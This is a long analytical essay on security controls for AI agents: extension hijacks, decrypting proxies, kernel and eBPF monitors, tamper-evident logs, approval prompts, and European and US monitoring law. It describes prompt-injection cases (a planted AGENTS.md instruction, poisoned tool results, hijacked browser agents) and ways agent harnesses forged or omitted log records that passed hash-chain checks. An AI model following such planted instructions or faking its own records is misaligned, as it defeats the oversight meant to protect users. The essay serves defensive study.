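Cyberhaven sells software that stops employees from moving company data where it does not belong. Its Chrome extension can block a transfer or ask the employee to explain it, according to SiliconANGLE's *Hackers compromise Chrome extensions with 400,000+ users* (2024). To do this, the extension needs access to the pages where people work.

On 24 December 2024, an attacker phished a Cyberhaven employee's login for the Chrome Web Store, then published a malicious version of the company's Chrome extension. Ting (2024), Cyberhaven's chief executive, reports in *Cyberhaven's Chrome extension security incident and what we're doing about it* that the malicious code was active for about 25 hours and reached browsers that updated automatically during that time. It could steal cookies and logged-in sessions for certain websites, and early findings suggested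 that the targets were social media advertising and AI platforms. Ting reports no compromise of the company's code-signing keys or build system, which the attacker did not need because access to the store was enough to publish the update.

Cyberhaven's *Final analysis* (2025) reports that the wider campaign may have compromised more than 30 other extensions, with over 2.6 million users in total. Cyberhaven has since removed the permanent access to the extension store that several of its senior developers had. It criticised the store for not letting it sign the extension itself. It planned to host the extension on its own servers, have other software on the device check that nobody had altered it, and let customers control when updates arrive.

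An extension's publisher can also use it against its users. The extension-security company Koi found that Urban VPN Proxy had collected people's conversations with AI chatbots since an automatic update in July 2025. Related extensions from the same publisher contained the same code, and altogether they had more than 8 million users. Urban VPN advertised an "AI protection" feature that checked prompts for personal data, but turning it off did not stop the collection. Koi sells protection against such extensions, so it has a commercial interest in the threat, but it published the extensions' identifiers and described the code in detail.

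24 Канал's *Шпион в браузере* (2026), a Ukrainian news report from July, describes a similar recent case in which an extension for improving prompts, with about 100,000 users, collected conversations from nine AI services.

Browser agents increase the risk from extensions, because an extension that can alter a page can also influence an agent that reads it. *BragJack Shows How Malicious Extensions Can Hijack AI Browser Agents* (Ofonagoro, 2026) reports that researchers showed this kind of manipulation in Chrome, Edge, Comet, Opera Neon and Claude in Chrome, in a demonstration rather than a known attack. An attacker who gained control of a security extension could use it the same way.

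### Proxies that weakened encryption

A decrypting proxy makes its own connection to the website, so the program behind the proxy depends on the quality of that second connection. Zakir Durumeric and colleagues presented a study of how well proxies make these connections at the NDSS computer security conference in 2017. They detected interception by comparing the browser named in a web request with the way the TLS connection began. A mismatch meant that other software had probably made the connection.

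"The Security Impact of HTTPS Interception" estimated that proxies or security software intercepted 4.0% of connections to Firefox's update servers, 6.2% of those to a group of shopping sites and 10.9% of US connections to the network company Cloudflare. Interception reduced the security of 97% of the intercepted Firefox connections, 32% of the shopping connections and 54% of the Cloudflare connections. Some products accepted outdated encryption or failed to check certificates properly. The program behind the proxy could not detect this because its own connection to the proxy appeared secure.

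Those results are old, and browsers and TLS have improved since, but the problem had not disappeared by 2020, when Louis Waked, Mohammad Mannan and Amr Youssef published tests of 13 network appliances. Four did not check websites' certificates at all, and eleven accepted certificates signed with MD5, which researchers had broken years earlier. An attacker on the network could have impersonated a website to everyone behind such an appliance.

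Neither study covers the newer proxies built for agents, so the percentages are weak evidence of how common the problem is in those proxies. The results are still a reason for a company to test a proxy's outgoing connections, for instance by checking that it refuses expired and forged certificates.

### A kernel driver that stopped Windows

CrowdStrike sells *endpoint detection and response* (EDR) software, which monitors a whole computer for signs of an attack. On Windows, part of it ran as a *driver*, code loaded into the kernel. On 19 July 2024, CrowdStrike sent out a faulty configuration update. According to the company's analysis, the update made the driver look for a 21st value in a list of 20, so it read memory beyond the end of the list.

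If this mistake occurs in an ordinary program, the operating system can end that program and keep running. Because it occurred in the kernel, Windows itself crashed, and many computers crashed again whenever they restarted. No attacker was involved, but the update affected 8.5 million devices by Microsoft's estimate. CrowdStrike withdrew it after 78 minutes, but people had to repair many of the computers by hand.

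Like Cyberhaven's malicious version, the update spread automatically before anyone noticed the problem. Releasing updates to a small group first would limit both kinds of damage, but would also delay protection against new attacks.

Microsoft responded with the Windows Resiliency Initiative, under which it required security companies in its partner programme to release updates gradually. In June 2025, it announced a private preview of a platform on which their products could run outside the kernel, like ordinary programs. The announcement did not include a ban on security companies' drivers in the kernel or a date for one. These companies have had reasons to keep their drivers there, because a driver can start early and is harder for malicious software to switch off.

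### What eBPF's checks leave in place

eBPF reduces the risk of this kind of crash in a different way. The monitor's programs still run in the kernel, but the verifier should reject one that could read past the end of a list, as CrowdStrike's driver did. A traditional driver goes through no equivalent check when it loads. The protection is not absolute, since the verifier and the rest of the kernel are also software and can contain errors.

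A program that passes the verifier could still block every attempt to open a file, which might make the computer as unusable as a crash would, even though Linux keeps running.

The daemon adds another risk because it, or a separate loader, needs high privilege to load eBPF programs into the kernel. An attacker who gained that privilege could copy other applications' messages before they are encrypted. Kashyap and colleagues cite earlier research on the abuse of eBPF privileges and treat the problem as separate from Argus. ActPlane likewise gives no guarantees if an attacker gains that privilege.

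Argus and ActPlane apply their rules only to the agent and the processes it starts, so a mistaken rule should stop only the agent's work. But this limit comes from how their developers wrote the programs, and an attacker with the same privilege could load programs without it.

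## What do the logs prove, and can the control itself be inspected?

If a company finds its credentials on an outside host, it may have only the logs from its security controls to work out what its agent did. How useful those logs are depends on what each entry can prove and whether anyone could have changed, omitted or invented entries. The company also has to decide how far to trust the control that wrote them, which is easier if outsiders can inspect it.

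### What a single entry establishes

| Placement | Example of an entry | What it establishes | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|---|
| Protocol boundary | The agent called `share_document` with an outsider's address, and the proxy allowed it | The request, its arguments and the decision | What the server then did |
| Browser | A form with these values left this page | The content and the site | Whether a person or an agent clicked, and what the site did next |
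| Network traffic, decrypted | A request uploaded this text to `files.example` | What left the machine, and the reply | Why, and often which program sent it |
| Operating system | Process 4127 opened the credentials file | The effect on the machine | The purpose |

According to the documentation of euno, an MCP proxy, a protocol log entry guarantees that the agent sent a call with certain arguments and that the policy allowed or refused it. The entry guarantees nothing about the server's internal actions, which need a separate record. The hidden deletion by `validate_patch` is one such action.

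The server's reply adds some evidence. *Epistemic Guard* (2026) describes a proxy that distinguishes four outcomes: the tool finished, the tool reported a failure, the server rejected the call before running it, or the server crashed partway through. After a crash, the log entry cannot show how much of the work the tool had already done.

A kernel log can show what happened during a tool call. Anand's *Auditing MCP Tool Calls at the Kernel Level* gives an invented example in which the application log shows `read_customer_data` completing successfully. The kernel log of the same call contains two policy violations, a blocked operation and an unexpected subprocess.

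Matching kernel events to MCP requests is difficult because the events carry process IDs, the requests carry their own IDs, and one server may handle many requests at once. Anand proposes that the server register the request it is working on, so that any process it starts inherits the request's ID. The match then depends on the server, which is a weakness if the server itself is under suspicion.

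### Tying an effect to the prompt behind it

AgentSight connects model replies to system events through process ancestry, timing and matching text, so it can fail to link a much later effect to the agent. For example, a manipulated agent might leave behind a script and a scheduled task. An hour after the agent exits, the system's scheduler runs the script, which connects to an attacker. The scheduler does not descend from the agent, and too much time has passed for timing to help.

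Bao, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *AgentLoupe*, address this by attaching a label to whatever the agent touches:

1. An eBPF probe on the encryption library detects a new prompt on its way to the model, and the kernel part of AgentLoupe gives the sending thread a number.
2. Every process that the thread starts inherits the number.
3. When a labelled process writes a file, AgentLoupe stores the number against that file.
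4. Any process that later opens or runs the file takes on the number, whether or not it descends from the agent. Labels also spread through network connections.

Each independent prompt gets a new number, because labels that spread without limit would end up grouping almost everything on the machine together. If the session had already picked up an older label from a file, AgentLoupe records a link between the two numbers and keeps their events separate.

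Bao and colleagues staged two attacks with Claude Code. In the scheduled-task attack, AgentLoupe traced the final network connection to the conversation that had produced the script. In the other, one session planted an instruction in an `AGENTS.md` file and a later session followed it. The label on the file connected the two sessions.

Over five runs of each task, AgentLoupe increased running time by 4.5% for studying a repository, 8.0% for writing code and 7.7% for compiling. AgentSight increased it by 4.5%, 2.5% and 1.7%. Most of the extra time on the last two tasks came from spreading the labels.

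Two staged attacks show that the method can work, but Bao and colleagues did not measure how often it links unrelated events or misses real links. They argue that AgentSight's design would have caused it to miss both attacks, but leave a side-by-side test for later. A label shows only that an event followed from a conversation. In action (b), an investigator could use it to trace the upload to the conversation in which the model asked for the script, but would still have to find the planted text there and work out that the developer never wanted the upload.

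### A hash chain with three entries

None of this helps if someone can quietly edit the log. A common protection is a *hash chain*. A *hash* is a short fingerprint that a program computes from data, and any change to the data almost certainly changes it. In a chain, each entry's hash covers both the entry and the hash before it:

```text
hash of entry n = H(hash of entry n-1, content of entry n)
```

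Here is a log with invented four-character hashes (real ones are much longer):

```text
1  read_file, config.yaml, allowed
   H(0000, entry 1) = 7a1c

2  share_document, visitor@outside.example, allowed
   H(7a1c, entry 2) = e490

3  read_file, notes.md, allowed
   H(e490, entry 3) = 52bd
```

If someone changes the address in entry 2 to `ana@firm.example`, an auditor who recomputes the hash gets `b36f`, which does not match the stored `e490`. If the editor stores `b36f` instead, entry 3 no longer matches, because its hash depended on `e490`. The editor could also recompute entry 3's hash and store the result, `08d2`, which would make the chain consistent again. Only an auditor who had kept entry 3's original hash, `52bd`, out of the editor's reach would then notice the change.

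Removing the last entry takes no recomputation, since entries 1 and 2 already form a valid chain. *BioFirewall* (2026), which describes a chained log for biosecurity screening, notes that a truncated log looks the same as one that never had more entries. Its verifier can therefore check the log against a final hash and an entry count stored elsewhere.

A signature adds protection only if the signing key is safe. The euno proxy signs each log entry with a key stored in the user's home folder. Other users' accounts cannot read the key, but an agent usually runs under the developer's own account. The proxy also signs each entry separately, so its signatures can reveal a changed entry but not a missing one.

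### Mandato's log

Racioppi's MCP proxy, Mandato, records every decision in a chain. Each record contains the time, the call, the version of the mandate that applied, the outcome and the result of each condition. If the person responsible later approves an action that Mandato refused, Mandato adds a new record and leaves the old one unchanged.

Mandato periodically computes a single hash over a batch of records and has an outside service timestamp it. An auditor could use these checkpoints to detect later edits without trusting the company that runs the proxy. That company could still suppress a record before the next checkpoint, so Racioppi suggests shorter intervals or a second signer. Racioppi eventually wants to use timestamp providers with a special status in EU law, so that courts would presume the checkpoints to be intact.

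Racioppi also expects the log to be complete, because the servers accept calls only from the proxy. This is reasonable for calls to those servers, but it does not cover the script in (b). The planned test will restart the proxy and interrupt its decision service while counting calls that reach a server without being logged, with a target of zero.

### Records written outside the agent

Mandato writes its log outside the agent's process. In *Hearsay*, Dai, Yang and colleagues (2026) measured how much that separation matters by giving the coding harness aider a hash chain over its own log and then making it write false records. In 14 runs it omitted a reply from the model, and in 14 others it added a made-up sentence. The chain passed verification in all 28 runs because aider had computed the hashes over the false log.

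A separate ledger exposed all 28. It combined records from two placements, a proxy that captured traffic between the harness and the model, and a monitor that captured the processes started and files changed. The researchers checked the log against the ledger for missing events and for entries with no matching event.

The same comparison showed that SWE-agent, a widely used harness, had left tool calls out of its log in 19 of 28 runs, a fault nobody had planted. It rejected some of the model's replies, such as those with several calls at once, and logged neither the reply nor the rejection. Dai and colleagues also had a language model audit 16 agent frameworks. It found none that kept a record an outsider could check without trusting the framework.

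Careful reading was a poor substitute for a second record:

| Method | Altered logs detected | Unaltered logs flagged |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 49% | 5% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 85% | 42% |
| Panel of people, by majority | 37% | 10% |
| Comparison with the ledger, rules fixed in advance | 64 of 66 | 0 of 84 |

The ledger's result comes from a different set of runs, but the gap between the results is too large for that to explain. The ledger's rules needed tuning for each log format. In an earlier test, the comparison flagged 37 of 115 unaltered logs until the researchers exempted more kinds of text. All the runs were short, at seven minutes or less.

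A further experiment shows why the ledger needed both placements. A modified harness changed a failing test result to a pass before it reached the model or the log, so the recorded model traffic also showed a pass. The monitor had recorded the test program's exit code, which exposed the change in all 11 runs where the test had failed.

A company that controls the ledger could still rewrite it. The ledger can be checked against the model provider's copies, and in this study all 708 copies matched it exactly.

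The signing key also has to be kept separate. *Epistemic Guard* removes its key from the settings an MCP server inherits, so a compromised server cannot forge receipts. *Tool Receipts, Not Zero-Knowledge Proofs* (2026) uses signed receipts to check what the agent tells the user. If the agent reports five search results but the receipt records three, the user can learn that the report is wrong.

### Events that nobody recorded

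A chain protects only the entries it contains, so it can be valid even when an event is missing. Zhao (2026), in *Auditable Claims about AI Agents*, illustrates this with a fictional firm that claims a person approves every external email its agent sends. The firm's three records are the agent's log, an authorisation server's list of approvals, and the mail gateway's list of deliveries.

One email has a confirmation in the agent's chat interface but no approval on the server. If the server's list is complete, this email disproves the claim. In another variation, the agent's log is signed and chained and passes every check, but it contains only three emails, while the gateway recorded four. The fourth might have come from the agent or from a person using the same account, so we can't tell from the records who sent it.

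Such a claim is therefore much easier to disprove than to support. One well-documented exception disproves it, but supporting it requires evidence that no unrecorded exception exists. Zhao proves, under stated assumptions, that signatures and chains on the agent's own records can never provide that evidence. An independent record can, if every relevant action has to pass through the component that writes it, which is complete mediation applied to evidence. For the shared document in (d), the document service's own list of shares would be a good choice, because it would include shares requested from a script as well as those sent through MCP.

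Zhao recommends that, before making a claim, a company write down the exact policy, the period, the records and who writes them. "Every action is logged" doesn't meet this standard because nobody can tell which records would disprove it.

### What Cowork's virtual machine hid

Isolating an agent can prevent independent software from recording what it does. The virtual machine that confined Claude Cowork also prevented customers' endpoint detection and response (EDR) software from monitoring activity inside it, so the software recorded only that a virtual machine was running. Companies that had to monitor their computers for compliance asked why. In May 2026, Anthropic offered event logs that administrators could retrieve afterwards, and acknowledged that these did not provide live monitoring.

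Anthropic's *Monitor Claude Cowork activity with OpenTelemetry* now describes a live stream of events to a company's own security systems. The events include tool calls, connected folders and whether a person approved each action. All events that follow from the same prompt share an identifier.

This closes part of the gap, but an administrator has to set up the stream, and by default it leaves out prompt text and tool inputs. For action (d), the default record would show a successful call to an MCP tool without naming the server, the tool or the recipient. Cowork also writes these events itself, whereas EDR would have provided a separate account of what the code did.

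Anthropic's *Compliance API coverage extends to Claude Cowork and Claude Code* announces fuller transcripts, in beta for Enterprise customers. These transcripts include prompts, replies and tool activity, but do not cover sessions on some other companies' cloud platforms.

Even a complete log may not reveal an attack. Anthropic warns that when a poisoned tool result leads an agent to send data out, the log shows only a successful, authorised call, with no sign of trouble. It therefore prefers to inspect results before the model reads them. The warning is slightly overstated for logs that keep tool results, because those logs would contain the planted text. An investigator would still need a reason to look there, and a default Cowork log would not contain the text.

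### Open code, closed code and remote services

How much a log can be trusted also depends on the program that wrote it, and some controls let customers examine more of that program than others do.

| Control | Can outsiders read the code? | Can a customer stay on a reviewed version? |
|---|---|---|
| Open-source proxy or sandbox | Yes | Yes, if it runs locally without automatic updates |
| Closed endpoint software, such as most EDR | Usually not | Only if the vendor lets customers hold back updates |
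| Remote gateway or inspection service | Usually not | No, because its operator can change it |

Saltzer and Schroeder argued in 1975 that a protection mechanism should not depend on keeping its design secret. Anthropic has published the code of its sandbox so that others can inspect it. Each release of Pipelock, an open-source proxy for agents, also comes with a list of components and a signed statement of how the release was built. Customers can use the statement to check that the program they downloaded came from the published code.

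Even when code is published, someone competent still has to review it. Docker's MCP Gateway is open source, yet the flaw that exposed the host remained through many versions. A signature does not replace that review. *Signed, Sealed, Leaked* (2026) explains that a signed release proves where the code came from but not what it does with the data it receives, and that any hidden routine is signed along with the rest.

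Customers can test what closed endpoint software blocks and watch where it connects. Those tests cannot rule out behaviour they never trigger, and an automatic update like CrowdStrike's may make the results obsolete.

Remote services are even harder to inspect. Anthropic points out that a customer can read a local tool's code and pin its version, but a remote tool can change at any time after approval. A remote gateway used as a control can change in the same way. *MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP systems, notes that the protocol has no built-in way to check that a tool is unchanged. It recommends storing hashes of approved definitions, but like mcp-context-protector's comparison of descriptions, this misses changes to hidden code that leave the definition the same. Installing a tool locally doesn't fully solve the problem, because some servers download part of their code while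 running.

### What detailed logs expose

Logs detailed enough to be useful can also expose sensitive data. A record of the upload in (b) could contain the stolen credentials, and AgentLoupe's records include the conversation with the model. Anthropic warns that tool details in Cowork's event stream may include sensitive values. Even with content turned off, the stream contains users' email addresses, folder paths and error messages, which sometimes repeat part of a request.

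Logs can also spread an attack. After Anthropic's February exercise, staff shared the working malicious prompt in Slack, and someone pointed out that internal agents read Slack. Anthropic added a marker to the discussion to detect whether an agent picked up the text. A company that asks an agent to review security logs has the same problem, because the logs can contain malicious prompts.

Some designs keep the log verifiable without permanently storing sensitive content in it. Mandato can store a hash of a sensitive argument, and the company can reveal the original later if a dispute requires it. If the value is predictable, such as an email address, the hash must include a random secret, or anyone could test likely addresses against it. *aiAuthZ* (2026) keeps each decision in the chain but erases the encrypted content after a set period. The log can still be verified because the chain covers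 hashes of the content, but nobody can later find out what an erased prompt or argument contained.

### Record-keeping under the EU AI Act

The EU AI Act requires logs for *high-risk* AI systems, which include certain uses in areas such as recruitment and certain regulated products such as medical devices. These systems must be able to record events automatically throughout their lifetime, and the records must help people identify risks and monitor how the system works (European Commission, *Article 12*). Providers must keep the logs they control for at least six months (Article 19, reproduced by artificialintelligenceact.eu). Organisations that use the systems have a similar duty (European Commission, *Article 26*).

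In July 2026, the European Union postponed these duties until 2 December 2027 for the high-risk uses listed in Annex III of the Act, and until 2 August 2028 for AI covered by the product laws in Annex I. Systems on the market before the relevant date are generally exempt unless their design changes significantly, but those intended for public authorities must comply by 2 August 2030.

A coding agent that repairs tests would probably not count as high-risk, while an agent that ranks job applicants could. Article 12, which applies to high-risk systems, does not mention hash chains, signatures or an independent log writer. Racioppi reads it as calling for logs whose completeness and integrity others can verify. Such logs are good practice, but the article's wording does not require them.

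A company could also keep the required logs and still be unable to answer a legal question. *From Runtime Records to Legal Findings* (2026) gives the example of whether protected data left a controlled environment. An entry showing that the agent sent a file answers this only if the log also records what kind of data the file contained and whether the destination was outside that environment. To show that a human could have intervened, the log would need to record who had the authority to stop the action and how much time they had.

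Technical standards may make the requirements more specific. Zhao reports that in September 2026 an international standard on AI logging had reached its final draft and a European one was awaiting approval.

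## Whose consent does deeper interception need?

A log of prompts, web pages or messages is also a record of people. Three different things go by the name of consent when a company wants to collect one:

- *Device approval* lets software run on a machine with a certain level of access. It may be a click on "Allow" or an administrator's password.
- *A legal basis* is the ground on which the law lets an employer monitor its staff. It need not be their consent.
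- *Third-party consent* would have to come from people who never use the machine, such as a colleague whose message the agent reads.

One party's consent does not cover the others. An administrator can approve monitoring on every laptop in a company without asking the laptops' users or the people who write to those users.

### Device approvals, from shallow to deep

The table lists the approvals roughly in order of the privilege they give. Employers can grant most of them through *device management*, a service for configuring computers and phones remotely.

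| What needs approval | Who approves it on a personal device | Can an employer do so silently? | How to withdraw it |
|---|---|---|---|
| A changed entry in the agent's configuration | Anyone who can edit the file | Yes, if it administers the computer | Restore the old entry |
| A browser extension | The user | Yes | Remove it, or have the employer take it off its list |
| A root certificate | The user, sometimes with an administrator's password | Yes | Remove the certificate or the profile that installed it |
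| A macOS system extension | An administrator | Yes | Uninstall it or remove the employer's approval |
| Full disk access on macOS | The user | Yes | Turn it off, or have the employer change its policy |
| Programs in the kernel | An administrator | On Linux, yes; on macOS, sometimes | An administrator unloads them |

Users normally see a list of permissions to accept when they install a browser extension, but Chrome's `force_installed` setting skips this step. *Apple Google Chrome Extension Deployment and Blocking Policy*, from the device management company Swif, describes the permissions as "granted implicitly" and says that Chrome uninstalls the extension once the employer takes it off the force-install list. Google's *Configure ExtensionSettings policy* also describes a milder setting that installs an extension automatically but lets the user disable it.

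*Force Enable Extension Without Using Group Policy* (Kettner and Jaiswal, 2024) discusses how Chrome keeps an extension added by other software disabled until the user enables it, unless a policy installed it. Chrome therefore lets whoever controls its policies decide for the user.

Root certificates work similarly. Apple's *Trust manually installed certificate profiles in iOS, iPadOS and visionOS* explains that an iPhone does not trust a manually installed certificate for TLS until the user also turns on trust in the settings. If the certificate comes through device management, the phone trusts it automatically and the user cannot change that. On a Mac, a user who installs a certificate profile manually has to review it in the settings and may need an administrator's password.

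macOS *system extensions* can monitor files and network traffic without running in the kernel. On an unmanaged Mac, an administrator has to approve each one. According to Apple's *System extensions in macOS*, an employer can instead approve a particular extension, or everything from one developer, without any action by the user. Removing that approval unloads the extension.

*Full disk access* is a separate permission to read files that macOS otherwise protects. An employer can grant it to Broadcom's monitoring software without a prompt, according to Broadcom's *Configuring MDM profiles for Full Disk Access for macOS 10.15*. Users cannot change permissions that their employer has set this way, according to Swif's *macOS Privacy Preferences PPPC Policy*. Mimecast's *macOS permissions for the insider risk agent* shows that one product needs a system extension, full disk access and an accessibility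 permission. The product uses the accessibility permission to report the title and address of browser tabs.

Apple no longer recommends running software in the kernel and makes it harder to approve. The user of an unmanaged Mac has to restart it while holding the power button, log in as an administrator and lower the computer's security setting. The user of a company Mac sometimes has to do the same, but if the company registered the Mac with Apple for automatic enrolment, device management can change the setting instead. The Mac still has to restart.

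On Linux, an employer with administrator rights can load an eBPF monitor without the developer noticing, and a developer without those rights cannot unload it.

How hard a control is to approve is a poor guide to how much it will read. A browser extension installed with one click can read a person's private email. Probes on an encryption library capture much the same text as TLS inspection, but they don't add a certificate that a user could find in the device's settings.

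MagicMirror sells an on-device control for AI applications. It recommends that customers add a certificate so that the product can inspect calls to model providers, but the certificate is optional. Without it, the product covers only programs that it can configure to send those calls through its proxy, and MagicMirror says these customers accept "narrower visibility". The company that buys the product makes this choice, not the employees whose prompts it reads.

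### Code that ran before the trust prompt

An approval is useless if the software acts before the user gives it. Between mid-2025 and January 2026, Anthropic received reports of three such flaws in Claude Code.

In the simplest case, a developer downloaded someone else's project to review a proposed change. The project's settings file defined a hook, a command for the harness to run automatically. Claude Code read the file as it started and ran the hook before asking whether the developer trusted the folder. In the other two flaws, Claude Code also processed material from a folder that the user had not yet trusted.

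Anthropic fixed all three by waiting for the user's answer before reading or running a project's configuration. It advises other developers to treat opening a project or loading its settings with the same suspicion as a request from the internet.

These flaws show why a configuration change deserves care, even though it requires the shallowest approval in the table. Hooks run outside Claude Code's sandbox, so a stranger's project can use one to attack the developer.

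### When "Always Allow" allows too much

Approvals can also cover more than the user intended. *Options, Not Clicks* (Li, Khabra and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent a question about a product. When the agent requests permission to search a sales folder for prices, the user clicks "Always Allow" for the search tool. Later, the agent uses the same tool to search the user's whole home folder, then emails sensitive files using an email tool the user has also approved. No new prompt appears, because the permission depends on the tool's name, not on the folder or the recipient.

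To measure how often this happens, the researchers collected 50 work sessions, containing 1,435 tool calls, from six developers at two companies. They labelled 291 of the calls, about one in five, as *boundary crossings*, meaning the call went beyond what the user had previously authorised. In one session, an agent that had been working in one project deleted a folder in another.

They then replayed the sessions with different approval systems:

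| Approval system | Boundary crossings detected (of 291) |
|---|---|
| "Always Allow" | 0 |
| Claude Code's auto mode | 6 |
| ConLeash, the researchers' own system | 278 |

ConLeash runs between the harness and its MCP servers. For each permitted call, it records the data's source, destination and sensitivity, and what the call changes. If a later call goes beyond those limits, ConLeash prompts the user again and offers choices such as "this file" or "this folder".

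The comparison favours ConLeash because the researchers defined a crossing by the same limits that ConLeash checks. Auto mode instead looks for dangerous actions, whatever the user approved earlier. Not every crossing was a mistake, since a developer may well want an agent to move on to a second project. The more useful finding is that ordinary work often goes beyond the original approval, and "Always Allow" can never detect this.

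A study with 16 users suggests why people choose "Always Allow" anyway. Thirteen said they used it just to dismiss prompts, and only three said they read prompts carefully. With ConLeash, participants made lasting choices, each with a limit, in 46.3% of their decisions, compared with 13.3% for lasting choices with ordinary prompts. Fifteen of the 16 preferred ConLeash.

The limits add delay, mostly because ConLeash uses a language model to classify each call. Classification took 4.69 seconds, while checking the result against the user's permissions took 8.2 milliseconds. Li and colleagues expect that preparing and storing classifications in advance would remove most of the delay.

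Chrome makes the user approve each remote debugging connection. *When your user is an AI agent* reports that developers have asked for Chrome to remember their answer. The Chrome team replied that it had no simple way to do this without also giving any program on the computer easy access to the user's data.

### Why employees' consent rarely counts in Europe

A developer who approves a tool call decides what the agent may do, but that approval doesn't settle whether an employer may record the developer's work.

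The European Union's General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR) requires a legal basis for any use of personal data. Consent is one such basis, but only if the person is free to refuse. *Opinion 2/2017 on data processing at work* (2017), from the Article 29 Working Party, a group of European data protection authorities, concludes that employees are seldom free to refuse because they depend on the employer who is asking. An employee's agreement is not valid consent if refusing could harm them.

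The Opinion adds that consent requires an active choice, so neither the presence of software nor an unchanged default setting counts as consent. An extension or root certificate installed through device management is therefore no evidence that the employee consented.

Employers usually have to rely on a *legitimate interest* instead, such as protecting customers' data. The monitoring must be necessary for that purpose, proportionate to the risk and as unintrusive as possible. Employers must also tell employees about it.

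The Article 29 Working Party applies this reasoning to an employer that wants to decrypt and inspect its staff's web traffic. It accepts network security as a legitimate interest but considers monitoring everything employees do online disproportionate. The employer should look for less invasive measures first. If some decryption is still strictly necessary, the Opinion recommends several limits:

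- The appliance should block suspicious traffic and let the user ask for a review, with no permanent log of employees' activity. If some logging is strictly necessary, it can store data only when there is an incident.
- It should leave private webmail, banking and health sites encrypted.
- Employees should know what kinds of traffic it monitors and who may read suspicious log entries.
- The employer could offer an unmonitored connection, such as free Wi-Fi, for private use.

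The Opinion also recommends prevention over detection. If blocking certain websites would solve the problem, the employer should block them instead of monitoring all communications. For agents, this favours a sandbox or an egress allowlist wherever either would be enough. In action (b), a sandbox could hide the credentials file and a filter could block the outside host without anyone reading the developer's messages. The shared document in (d) goes through an approved service, so an employer has a better reason to inspect the request. Even then, an MCP proxy might be enough and handle less personal data than a proxy that decrypts all traffic.

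Reusing the data is another problem. The Opinion gives the example of an employer that installs a system to protect property and then uses it to monitor staff performance. MagicMirror's platform combines security functions with productivity and proficiency metrics and figures for each user's spending on AI models. A security justification for collecting prompts would probably not cover the metrics or spending figures.

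### What a French regulator expects of a decrypting proxy

More recent guidance from France's data protection authority, CNIL, covers proxies that filter employees' web traffic and may decrypt it. The *Recommandation sur le déploiement d'un serveur mandataire web filtrant* (2026) is not binding, but it gives employers a fairly concrete standard.

CNIL accepts legitimate interest as a legal basis for such a proxy, but doubts that the GDPR's general duty to keep data secure can by itself oblige an employer to install one. It recommends that the proxy leave traffic to low-risk sites encrypted, such as those of banks, health services and public authorities. The proxy should not keep the content of requests unless it detects malicious code. Logs should normally be kept for between six months and a year.

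CNIL also recognises that web addresses can reveal personal data. Decryption exposes each page's full address, which may contain a username or even a password. If the proxy uses its vendor to classify an unfamiliar site, it should send only the domain name.

The recommendation covers only part of what a company would want from a proxy for agents. It applies to malicious incoming material but excludes the analysis of outgoing traffic and data loss prevention products. CNIL's *Consultation sur le projet de recommandation sur le déploiement d'un serveur mandataire* (2026) confirms that endpoint detection and response software is also out of scope. If a company wanted a proxy that scans uploads for stolen credentials, or a monitor that records the whole computer, it would need a separate justification for each.

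### The Bărbulescu case

*Bărbulescu v. Romania*, from the European Court of Human Rights, is the leading European judgment on employers reading employees' messages. Bogdan Bărbulescu worked in sales and, at his company's request, set up a Yahoo Messenger account to answer customers. In July 2007, the company recorded his messages for about a week. When he denied using the account privately, it showed him a 45-page transcript that included intimate messages to his fiancée and messages to his brother. The company then dismissed him for breaking its ban on private use.

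The Romanian courts upheld the dismissal. In 2017, the European Court of Human Rights ruled by eleven votes to six that those courts had failed to protect the employee's right to respect for his private life and correspondence. The company had told him not to use its equipment for private purposes, but apparently had not told him in advance that it might read the content of his messages. The Court held that an employer's rules cannot reduce private social life at work "to zero".

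The judgment did not ban monitoring. It set out what national courts should examine:

- whether the employer gave clear notice before the monitoring began
- how much it monitored, for how long, and how many people had access to the results
- what reasons it had, with stronger reasons needed for reading content
- whether a less intrusive method would have worked
- what happened to the employee as a result
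- what safeguards the employee had

The Court distinguished the flow of communications from their content. A network filter that records destinations differs from a proxy that decrypts requests in much the same way, so decryption needs a stronger justification. But the Article 29 Working Party warns that an analysis of destinations can be as invasive as reading the content, for example if it reveals an employee's habits.

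### Works councils

In some European countries, an employer also needs the agreement of a *works council*, a body that represents its employees. Germany's Works Constitution Act gives the council a say over technical systems designed to monitor employees' behaviour or performance. German courts apply this to systems capable of such monitoring, even if the employer has another purpose. A log that links an agent's actions to named developers could easily count as such a system.

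A security control may need the works council's agreement even when the AI tool it monitors does not. In January 2024, the Hamburg Labour Court refused to stop a company from letting its staff use ChatGPT through their own accounts, partly because the employer had no access to their activity in those accounts. That reason would no longer apply if a control recorded their prompts for the employer.

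CNIL recommends involving employee representatives even where French law does not require it. The Article 29 Working Party argues that technical staff often write monitoring policies and tend to focus more on security than on employees' privacy, so it recommends asking a representative sample of employees to help judge whether the monitoring is necessary.

### Consent and notice in the United States

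Consent plays a larger role in American law. The federal Wiretap Act, which Congress extended to electronic communications in 1986, generally prohibits intercepting their content. It allows interception if one party to the communication consented beforehand, unless the purpose is to commit a crime or another legal wrong. Courts have sometimes inferred consent when an employer announced its monitoring and the employee kept using the system.

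Under federal law, an employee's consent can cover a message from someone who doesn't know about the monitoring. Some states are stricter. California generally requires consent from everyone involved in a confidential communication, so a company with customers or staff there cannot rely on the federal rule alone.

Where a control sits may also affect whether the Wiretap Act covers it, because courts have generally applied the act to messages captured during transmission. A decrypting proxy fits that description well, but it is less clear whether the description fits a probe that copies text just before a program encrypts and sends it. A monitor that only records which files a process opens is further from what the act usually deals with.

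New York requires notice instead of consent. Since May 2022, private employers that monitor email, phone calls or internet use have had to tell new employees in writing, obtain their acknowledgement and post a notice at work. The law exempts systems that manage the type or volume of traffic, do not target an individual and serve only to maintain or protect the computer system. A simple destination filter might be exempt, but a product that reports on each employee's use of AI probably would not be.

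California's general privacy law also gives employees rights over their personal data. *Web Filtering* (2025), a note by the law firm Fox Rothschild, recommends CNIL's draft guidance to employers in California as well as Europe, including its advice to limit decryption and not keep the content of requests.

Most of these American and European rules predate coding agents and were written with people's emails and browsing in mind. Courts will have to decide how far they apply to a prompt or to a message that an agent wrote.

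### People who never agreed to anything

Bărbulescu's fiancée and brother did not work for his employer and had not signed its rules, but the company read their messages too. The Court ruled only on his rights, because he had brought the case.

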